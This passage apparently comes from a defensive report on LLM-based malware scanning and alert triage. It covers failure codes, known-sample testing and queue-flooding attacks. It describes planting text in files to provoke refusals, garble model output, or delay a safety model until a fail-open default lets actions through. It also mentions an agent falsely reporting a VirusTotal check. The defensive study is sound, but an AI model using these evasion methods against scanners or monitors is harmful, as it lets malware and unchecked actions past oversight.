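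Operators should therefore break down each code by file type, source and model version, and record the reasoning setting too. They should limit the number of groups, because with 50 groups like this one, that threshold would cause a false alarm about every three weeks.

The pattern across groups often points to the cause:

| Pattern | Likely explanation |
|---|---|
| Refusals rise for every file type after a model update | The provider changed its safeguards |
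| Refusals rise for one file type or publisher while the model stays the same | Planted text, or a new kind of legitimate file |
| Timeouts rise everywhere | A fault at the provider or in the network |
| Timeouts or truncation rise for one source | Padding, or unusually large files |
| Malformed output rises after a change of reasoning setting | The new setting |

The last pattern has appeared in tests. In Talos's log test, Claude Sonnet 4.6 followed the required format every time at its low and medium settings, but broke it in 10 of 27 attempts at high and 15 of 29 at maximum. That test contained no text planted to disrupt the format. In Cloudflare's testing, by contrast, frontier models sometimes returned garbled answers after reading a thousand planted comments.

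A falling refusal rate also deserves attention, because the provider may have improved the model or the pipeline may have started recording refusals as something else.

### Tests with known samples

Regular tests with known files can distinguish these possibilities. A useful set would include ordinary malware, harmless programs, an oversized file, a harmless file with a fake error message, and harmless files with text that has caused refusals before. The operator records the acceptable verdicts and status codes for each file, then runs the set daily and before every change of model, prompt or setting.

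The tests should cover the surrounding software as well as the model. A programmer can replace the model with a stand-in that returns an empty reply, an unknown verdict, half an answer or no reply, and confirm that the pipeline holds the file each time. These tests take little effort and require no hostile text, and they would have exposed the fault that Weng and colleagues found in Gemini CLI.

An agent's operator also has to compare its final answer with the record of its tool calls. Elastic, a search and security software company, tests models against an intrusion staged in a working copy of its product and records every tool they call. Elastic warns that a model can call a malicious program clean and describe a VirusTotal result it never looked up. Such an answer looks complete, so none of the six codes would flag it.

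Finding no failures in a small test set is weak evidence that the system is reliable. If 300 different files produce no failures, the true failure rate could still be about 1%, even if those files represent real samples well. Attackers will also write texts that the test set doesn't contain, so operators should add examples from real incidents to it.

### Flooding the queue

If every missing verdict goes to an analyst, attackers can overload the analysts. Someone could upload 5,000 harmless files with refusal-provoking text and hide one malicious file among them. At the 60% rate from the example, analysts would receive 3,000 extra files, or 500 hours of work. In *From Shield to Target*, Zhou, Wang and colleagues (2026) used planted text to delay a safety model past a 30-second limit. Defaulting to "allow" then let unchecked actions through, while defaulting to "block" stopped 34 of 55 actions.

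Flooding is a serious objection to escalation without limits, but a weaker one to failing closed, because an attacker who floods a package marketplace gets a long queue in which the malicious file waits without reaching users. The danger is that the operator starts releasing files to shorten the queue, so no rule should clear files just because too many are waiting.

The filtered retry can put most of the flood at the back of the queue. If the second request wrongly flagged 6% of the harmless files, as Gemini 3.1 Pro did in the test by Sava and colleagues, 180 of the 3,000 would go to the front, which is 30 hours of work instead of 500. The malicious file would probably be at the front too, since the same model caught most malware, though that test used Windows programs, not filtered scripts.

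A flood of files is easier to handle when they contain the same planted text, because software can group them and an analyst can examine a few and reject the whole group. Clearing a whole group this way is unsafe, because the attacker may have put the one malicious file in it. Analysts will occasionally reject a legitimate project, such as a collection of test prompts, so publishers need a way to appeal.

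Limits for each source protect other publishers from a flood of escalations. If each new publisher can have at most five files awaiting review, an attacker needs 600 accounts to create 3,000 escalations. Established publishers can have a separate queue, though attackers sometimes take over established accounts. The operator should also cap the money spent on retries for each source, since a flood that triggers three model calls per file triples the bill even if no analyst sees the files.

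An attacker might instead plant the text in someone else's software, for example by contributing to a popular project, so that the scanner holds the software's next release. The marketplace can keep the previous version available while an analyst reviews the new one. This limits the damage unless the new version fixes an urgent flaw, in which case the analyst should review it first.

Flooding is more dangerous in alert triage because an intrusion continues while its alert waits, whereas a held file does no harm. In a newsletter from August 2026, Cisco Talos warns that handing refusals to people takes time and may let an attacker finish the attack. For the most serious alerts, the operator therefore needs fixed rules that act without a verdict, for example by disconnecting a machine or suspending an account. The operator also needs to reserve some analyst time for these alerts.
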